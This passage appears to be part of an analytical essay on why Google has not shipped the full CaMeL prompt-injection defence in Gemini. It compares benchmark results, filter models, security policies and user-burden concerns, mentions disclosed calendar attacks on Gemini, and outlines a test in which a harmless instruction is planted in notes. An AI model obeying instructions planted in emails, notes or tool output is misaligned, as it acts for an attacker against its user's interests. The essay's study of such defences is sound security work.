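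A model's own caution can also make it less useful. Claude Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks in MultiAgentDojo, even though the data contained no attack. Peters-Gill and colleagues suspect that it recognized the benchmark as a test of prompt injection, so it may refuse far less in normal use.

Blocking every attack in a benchmark is better evidence of security for CaMeL than for a filter, because the part of CaMeL's protection that comes from the fixed plan doesn't depend on recognizing an attack. Bhagwatkar and colleagues' *Sanitizer*, a filter model that removes suspicious instructions from everything the tools return, appears to beat CaMeL outright. It completed 74.1 percent of the tasks and let none of the benchmark's attacks through, but those attacks are fixed, and Bhagwatkar and colleagues consider them weak. Another filter, PIGuard, blocked every fixed attack on GPT-4o-mini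 in Ma and colleagues' tests, but 28.0 percent succeeded once the attacker could adapt.

The same weakness in the tests can make CaMeL look pointless. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks in MultiAgentDojo without any added defense, so on that benchmark CaMeL reduced its usefulness by 13.4 points without preventing any attacks. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding that GPT-5.5 is immune, since large tests with adaptive attackers have found successful attacks on every leading model they included.

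A fair comparison would run the same model on the same tasks, once with all of Gemini's layers and once with CaMeL and realistic policies, against attackers who adapt to each. It would count the questions each system asks users and have real people answer them. It would also need more tasks in which outside content should determine the next step. AgentDyn, a newer benchmark described in *StepGuard* (2026), is better suited to this than AgentDojo because it includes helpful third-party instructions and longer tasks that require replanning.

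Google is in the best position to run such a test, because outsiders can attack Gemini but can't switch off its layers one at a time. The test would still produce at least three numbers: tasks completed, attacks that succeeded, and questions asked. Combining them into one ranking requires a judgment about how many failed tasks are acceptable to prevent one leak. A law firm would probably accept far more failures than someone planning a holiday.

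## What Google has written about why CaMeL was not shipped whole

Google does not appear to have explained publicly why Gemini doesn't use the full CaMeL design. Lost usefulness, the work of writing security policies, and constant questions to users are all plausible reasons. Google's staff have written about each as a general problem, but they don't appear to have publicly linked any of them to a decision about CaMeL.

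That statement is based on a search of Google's papers and product posts on agent security, and of the summary of a Google Research post on open problems in the field. A search for comments on agent security from Google to NIST, the US standards agency, found none. Talks and interviews, where an engineer may well have given a reason, were not searched.

### What CaMeL's designers conceded

The CaMeL paper has a section titled "So, are prompt injections solved now?", which Willison quotes, and its answer is no. The paper names two practical limits: users have to write and maintain security policies, and the system burdens them while it runs. It adds that balancing security with a good user experience is hard, especially because of user fatigue and *declassification*, which means releasing data to someone its tags would otherwise exclude.

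Bob's proposal has to be declassified even when nobody is attacking, because its tag doesn't list him as a reader. Either the user decides each time and gets tired of being asked, or someone has to write a policy.

Willison was enthusiastic about CaMeL but "deeply nervous" about any system that requires ordinary users to think about security policies. He wrote that after two decades in application security, he still hadn't fully figured out the permissions system in Amazon's cloud. He hoped for a version of CaMeL with well-chosen defaults and a clear interface, which would move most of the work from the user to the company that makes the assistant.

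The CaMeL paper describes these problems as limits of a research system, and it calls CaMeL a "practical defense". The paper shows that Google's researchers knew about the policy and user problems from the start, but not that they thought those problems ruled out using CaMeL in products.

The code released with the paper carries a stronger disclaimer. According to *camel-prompt-injection*, a summary of the repository on the open-source tracking site SourcePulse, the code is a research artifact for reproducing the paper's results and "not a Google product". The interpreter may have bugs and may not be fully secure, and Google's researchers plan no support or bug fixes. This account is secondhand, but it fits what Garby and colleagues found when they examined the interpreter.

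The notice shows that nobody should run the released code in a product. It is much weaker evidence about Google's plans for the design, because Google attaches similar disclaimers to much of the code its researchers release. If a product team had adopted CaMeL, it would probably have written a new interpreter inside Google's own systems and left the public repository unchanged.

Google treats the two kinds of software differently in its reward programs. It offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating a breach of the security boundaries around Chrome's agent, according to Parker. CaMeL's code isn't eligible for Google's reward program for open-source software, according to SourcePulse.

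### Two papers from May 2025

Two months after CaMeL, Google DeepMind announced its white paper on training Gemini to resist injections, *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, 2025). The researchers wrote that such hardening "should certainly never be relied upon in isolation". They mentioned CaMeL but left combining it with a hardened model to future work.

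In the documents found, this is the closest Google's researchers come to discussing CaMeL and Gemini's defenses together, and they treat the two as compatible. Combining them would make sense, because a hardened quarantined model would be less likely to write the false summaries that CaMeL can't prevent.

"Future work" is a common phrase in research papers and doesn't commit anyone to doing the work, but it is evidence that Google DeepMind did not compare the two approaches in early 2025 and reject CaMeL. Shi and colleagues report no such comparison, and the eight add-on defenses they tested were all filters, prompts or checks around an ordinary agent.

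Díaz and colleagues come closest to giving a general reason in their paper on agent security from the same month. They write that restrictions enforced by classical software "lack the contextual awareness needed for versatile agents and can overly restrict utility". They also warn that comprehensive policies for a large range of actions are "complex and difficult to scale". Both objections could apply to CaMeL, but they never mention it by name.

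The first objection applies less to CaMeL than to a simple rule, because CaMeL's tags supply some of the missing context, such as whether a recipient's address came from the user or from a document.

Díaz and colleagues' second objection applies fully to CaMeL, because every protection it gives to data depends on a policy. But they don't conclude that Google should avoid policies, since policy engines are the first layer of their own design. They also promise a longer white paper with more technical detail. If Google has published it, that would be a good place to look for an explanation.

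### What the product posts mention and leave out

Google doesn't discuss CaMeL in its posts about Gemini itself. It describes five protections in the body of its June 2025 post without referring to CaMeL, which its own laboratory had published three months earlier. Gavish didn't mention CaMeL in April 2026, and Google doesn't mention it in its latest post on Gemini's defense in depth.

This kind of silence is usually weak evidence, because product posts describe the protections a product has, and companies rarely list the designs they decided against. Security teams also leave out details that might help attackers.

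Gavish's silence about CaMeL in his post on Workspace is a little more informative, because Google has credited the design elsewhere. Parker wrote in December 2025 that CaMeL had partly inspired Chrome's User Alignment Critic, and Berschadski repeated the credit for business customers in August 2026. Gavish published his post between those two. If Workspace had adopted CaMeL by then, his team would have had little reason to hide the name and some reason to advertise it.

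The posts' descriptions of Google's defenses are stronger evidence than their silence. In the June 2025 design, Google surrounds emails and files with reminders to ignore any commands in them. Those reminders are necessary only if the model that follows the user's request also reads the emails. In the latest design, classifiers scan search results, web pages, emails and files "before external content and tool outputs reach the planner". The planner therefore reads whatever the classifiers let through. CaMeL's central rule is that the model that writes the plan never reads such content, so the agent in the latest post can't be using the full design.

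The most recent relevant document, Google Research's *Open and Emergent Problems in Agentic Privacy and Security* (5 October 2026), introduces a workshop report and is about what rules agents should follow. In it, Eugene Bagdasarian and Marco Gruteser start from *contextual integrity*, the theory that whether information is private depends on the setting it came from. For example, a patient's diagnosis may properly go from the patient to a doctor, but not from the doctor to the patient's employer.

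Google researchers Bagdasarian and Gruteser want such norms to constrain agents. A year and a half after the CaMeL paper, they still considered this an open problem, with research questions at the level of the system, the model and the user. Their summary doesn't explain Google's product choices, but it is relevant to CaMeL because CaMeL's interpreter can enforce a norm only after someone has expressed it as a policy.

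### Researchers who worked on both

At least five of CaMeL's authors also co-wrote one of the two papers from May 2025. Chongyang Shi, who is listed first, Jamie Hayes, Ilia Shumailov and Andreas Terzis wrote the white paper on hardening with ten others. Christoph Kern wrote the paper on agent security with two others. None of the three people who signed the posts on Workspace and Chrome co-wrote the CaMeL paper.

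The overlap shows that people working on Gemini's security knew about CaMeL, so unfamiliarity can't explain why Google didn't ship it whole. It also gives more weight to some of the general complaints. Díaz and colleagues call comprehensive policies hard to scale, and one of them had recently helped design CaMeL, which needs such policies.

But writing a paper about Gemini doesn't give a researcher control over what goes into Gemini. Product managers, engineers and lawyers, who may have written nothing about CaMeL, also have a say. The overlap also doesn't show that the five changed their minds. A researcher can work on hardening the current model because it needs protection now, and still hope for a better architecture later.

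Papers that share authors with CaMeL can still take different positions. Several of CaMeL's designers co-wrote the June 2025 paper on design patterns, which sets a stricter standard than the Google paper by Kern and his co-authors had a few weeks earlier. Willison noticed the contrast and called the Google paper's approach "less strident".

Shumailov has since left Google DeepMind. According to the announcement of his talk *Is it even possible to defend AI agents against attacks in practice?*, scheduled for 28 October 2025 in Cambridge, he was a senior research scientist there "until recently" and now runs AI Sequrity, which builds security tools. In the abstract, he writes that prompt injection makes agents hard to deploy in practice.

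The announcement doesn't support reading his departure as a sign that Google had lost interest in CaMeL. Researchers leave large laboratories for many reasons, and the growing demand for agent security would have been reason enough. The company does show that one of CaMeL's designers thought customers would pay for better protection. It doesn't show whether Google had turned his ideas down, though he may have answered that in the talk.

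### How well the documents support each explanation

Google has not stated a reason, so outsiders can only compare each plausible explanation with what Google has published. In the table, "fairly good" means that CaMeL's designers and other Google staff have both described the problem, "moderate" means that Google's staff have described something close to it, and "weak" means that the explanation rests almost entirely on inference. No explanation is rated "strong", which would require Google to give it as a reason.

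| Explanation | Who describes the problem | Support |
|---|---|---|
| Policies are too hard to write and maintain | CaMeL's designers; Díaz and colleagues | fairly good |
| The user would face too many questions | CaMeL's designers; Parker; Google in its latest post | fairly good |
| Hard limits make an agent less useful | Díaz and colleagues | moderate |
| Users' tasks are too open-ended for a fixed plan | Díaz and colleagues, indirectly | moderate |
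| The design wasn't ready for a product | the repository's notice, as summarized by SourcePulse; Shi and colleagues, indirectly | moderate for 2025, weak for late 2026 |
| It would be too slow or expensive | CaMeL's designers, who measured the extra computing | weak |
| Google thinks the layers are good enough | nobody, in so many words | weak |

**Policy upkeep** is a well-supported problem, but Google already writes policies for the central engine that Gavish describes. Upkeep therefore explains the decision not to ship CaMeL whole only if CaMeL's policies would be much harder to write, and there is a case that they would be. Google could write a rule such as "ask before any purchase over $100" once for everyone, while a rule about Bob's proposal depends on what each user wants to share and with whom.

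The work of maintaining policies gives Google a good reason not to turn CaMeL on for everyone, but a weaker reason not to offer it to businesses at all. An administrator who can already forbid emails to outside addresses could also write CaMeL policies for the same tools, and a large customer might want to.

The concern about asking users questions recurs in Google's product posts. Parker plans to adjust Chrome's limits on websites "to reduce unnecessary friction while improving security". In its latest post, Google argues that human oversight works in practice only if Gemini doesn't interrupt the user during routine research.

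It isn't clear, though, that CaMeL would show users more questions than Gemini does now. Its tags could remove some of the questions Gemini already shows, but values taken from emails and web pages would trigger questions more often. Which effect is larger depends on how people use the assistant, and only Google has the data to find out.

Nearly every security measure reduces usefulness somewhat, so this explanation depends on how much usefulness CaMeL loses. The designers reported a fairly small loss on AgentDojo, but later tests with policies or on real websites found much larger ones. Díaz and colleagues couldn't have known about those later tests in May 2025, and they give no figures of their own. Their remark about restricting utility shows that Google's security engineers were worried about the problem, but not that they had measured it in CaMeL.

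The evidence on **open-ended tasks** comes mostly from the examples Google chooses. In the electric-bill task, Google's agent can't determine in advance that the answer will be a heat pump, so it has to revise its plan as it gathers information. Díaz and colleagues acknowledge that planning in a loop is riskier. Google built its agents this way anyway, which suggests that it highly valued the flexibility.

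Some of Google's business examples are much less open-ended. Berschadski describes an agent that logs in to several billing sites each month, downloads the invoices and checks them against each other. The sites are known and the steps repeat, so a company could test a fixed plan before relying on it, though changes to a website would still break the plan from time to time. This is close to the narrow, predictable work that suits CaMeL, so the open-ended nature of people's requests can't explain why Google doesn't describe using CaMeL anywhere.

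**Readiness** is probably a good explanation for the first few months. In spring 2025 CaMeL was a new design with an interpreter that its makers wouldn't guarantee, and the model writing the plans had to be very good at programming. Later models lost less from planning in advance, and other researchers showed how to repair faults in the tracking of tags. By late 2026, any lack of readiness has to come from something else, such as the absence of good default policies.

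Google's product posts don't mention CaMeL's **delay and cost**. CaMeL needs almost three times as many tokens as an ordinary agent, which would be a serious expense for a company with as many users as Google. But Gemini's layers use extra models too, and Google hasn't published what those models cost, so it is not clear that CaMeL would be more expensive than the existing protections.

The last explanation, **confidence in the layers**, conflicts with much of what Google's staff have written. Shi and colleagues, Gavish, and Google in its latest post all acknowledge that their defenses have limits.

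Google has released agents that can read email from strangers and act on the user's accounts. Somebody there must have judged the remaining risk acceptable, at least with the user watching, even if they thought the defenses were imperfect. Google hasn't said what failure rate it would accept.

Another possible reason is that agents can make mistakes without an attacker. Díaz and colleagues give the example of a user who has more than one Mike in their contacts and tells the agent to "email Mike about the project update." The agent may pick the wrong one and send him something confidential. CaMeL's tags wouldn't reliably catch this, because both addresses come from a trusted list. An agent can also misread a button on a complicated website and buy something by accident.

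Google would need checks for such errors whether or not it adopted CaMeL, so it was probably choosing between the layers alone and the layers plus CaMeL, with the drawbacks of both. That makes the decision easier to understand, because CaMeL would be worth adding only for the attacks it stops that the other layers miss. No Google document found makes this argument about CaMeL.

The documents best fit a decision with several causes, mainly the work of writing policies and the burden on users. These two are hard to separate, because good default policies would spare users many of the questions. This reading could easily be wrong. A product team might have tried CaMeL on real Gemini requests and dropped it for a reason no outsider has thought of, or might never have tried it.

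### Whether the design really stayed in research

Chrome is the obvious example of part of CaMeL's design reaching a product. Like CaMeL, Chrome's critic relies on a model kept away from untrusted content. That idea goes back to Willison's two-model pattern, and Parker credits both Willison and CaMeL. Neither Parker nor Berschadski describes Chrome as using CaMeL's own additions, such as the tags and the interpreter.

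Berschadski's post credits only CaMeL and leaves out the older pattern. The post accurately says "partially", but a business customer who reads nothing else could easily miss that word and think Chrome's agent has CaMeL's guarantees.

Parker presents Agent Origin Sets as an extension of Chrome's long-standing separation between websites. They restrict data flow, as CaMeL does, but he doesn't credit CaMeL for them. Two teams could easily have arrived at similar rules separately, because restricting where data may go is a much older idea than either system.

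One idea behind CaMeL has reached a Google product, but the complete design hasn't appeared in any product that Google has described publicly. Google could still be using CaMeL in an internal tool, in a trial with a few customers, or in a single Workspace feature that its posts don't cover in detail. The tool-chaining rules in Workspace might also track more than Gavish describes.

In both calendar attacks that researchers disclosed, Gemini took actions that a fixed plan would have ruled out, so those features can't have had CaMeL's full protection at the time. This evidence doesn't depend on Google's descriptions.

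Outsiders can repeat this kind of test as Gemini changes by giving it a request such as "summarize my notes" from an account they own, planting a harmless extra instruction in the notes, and watching which tools it calls. If the extra action happens, the plan wasn't fixed in advance. A refusal would be much harder to interpret, because a classifier, the model's training or a CaMeL interpreter could each have produced it.
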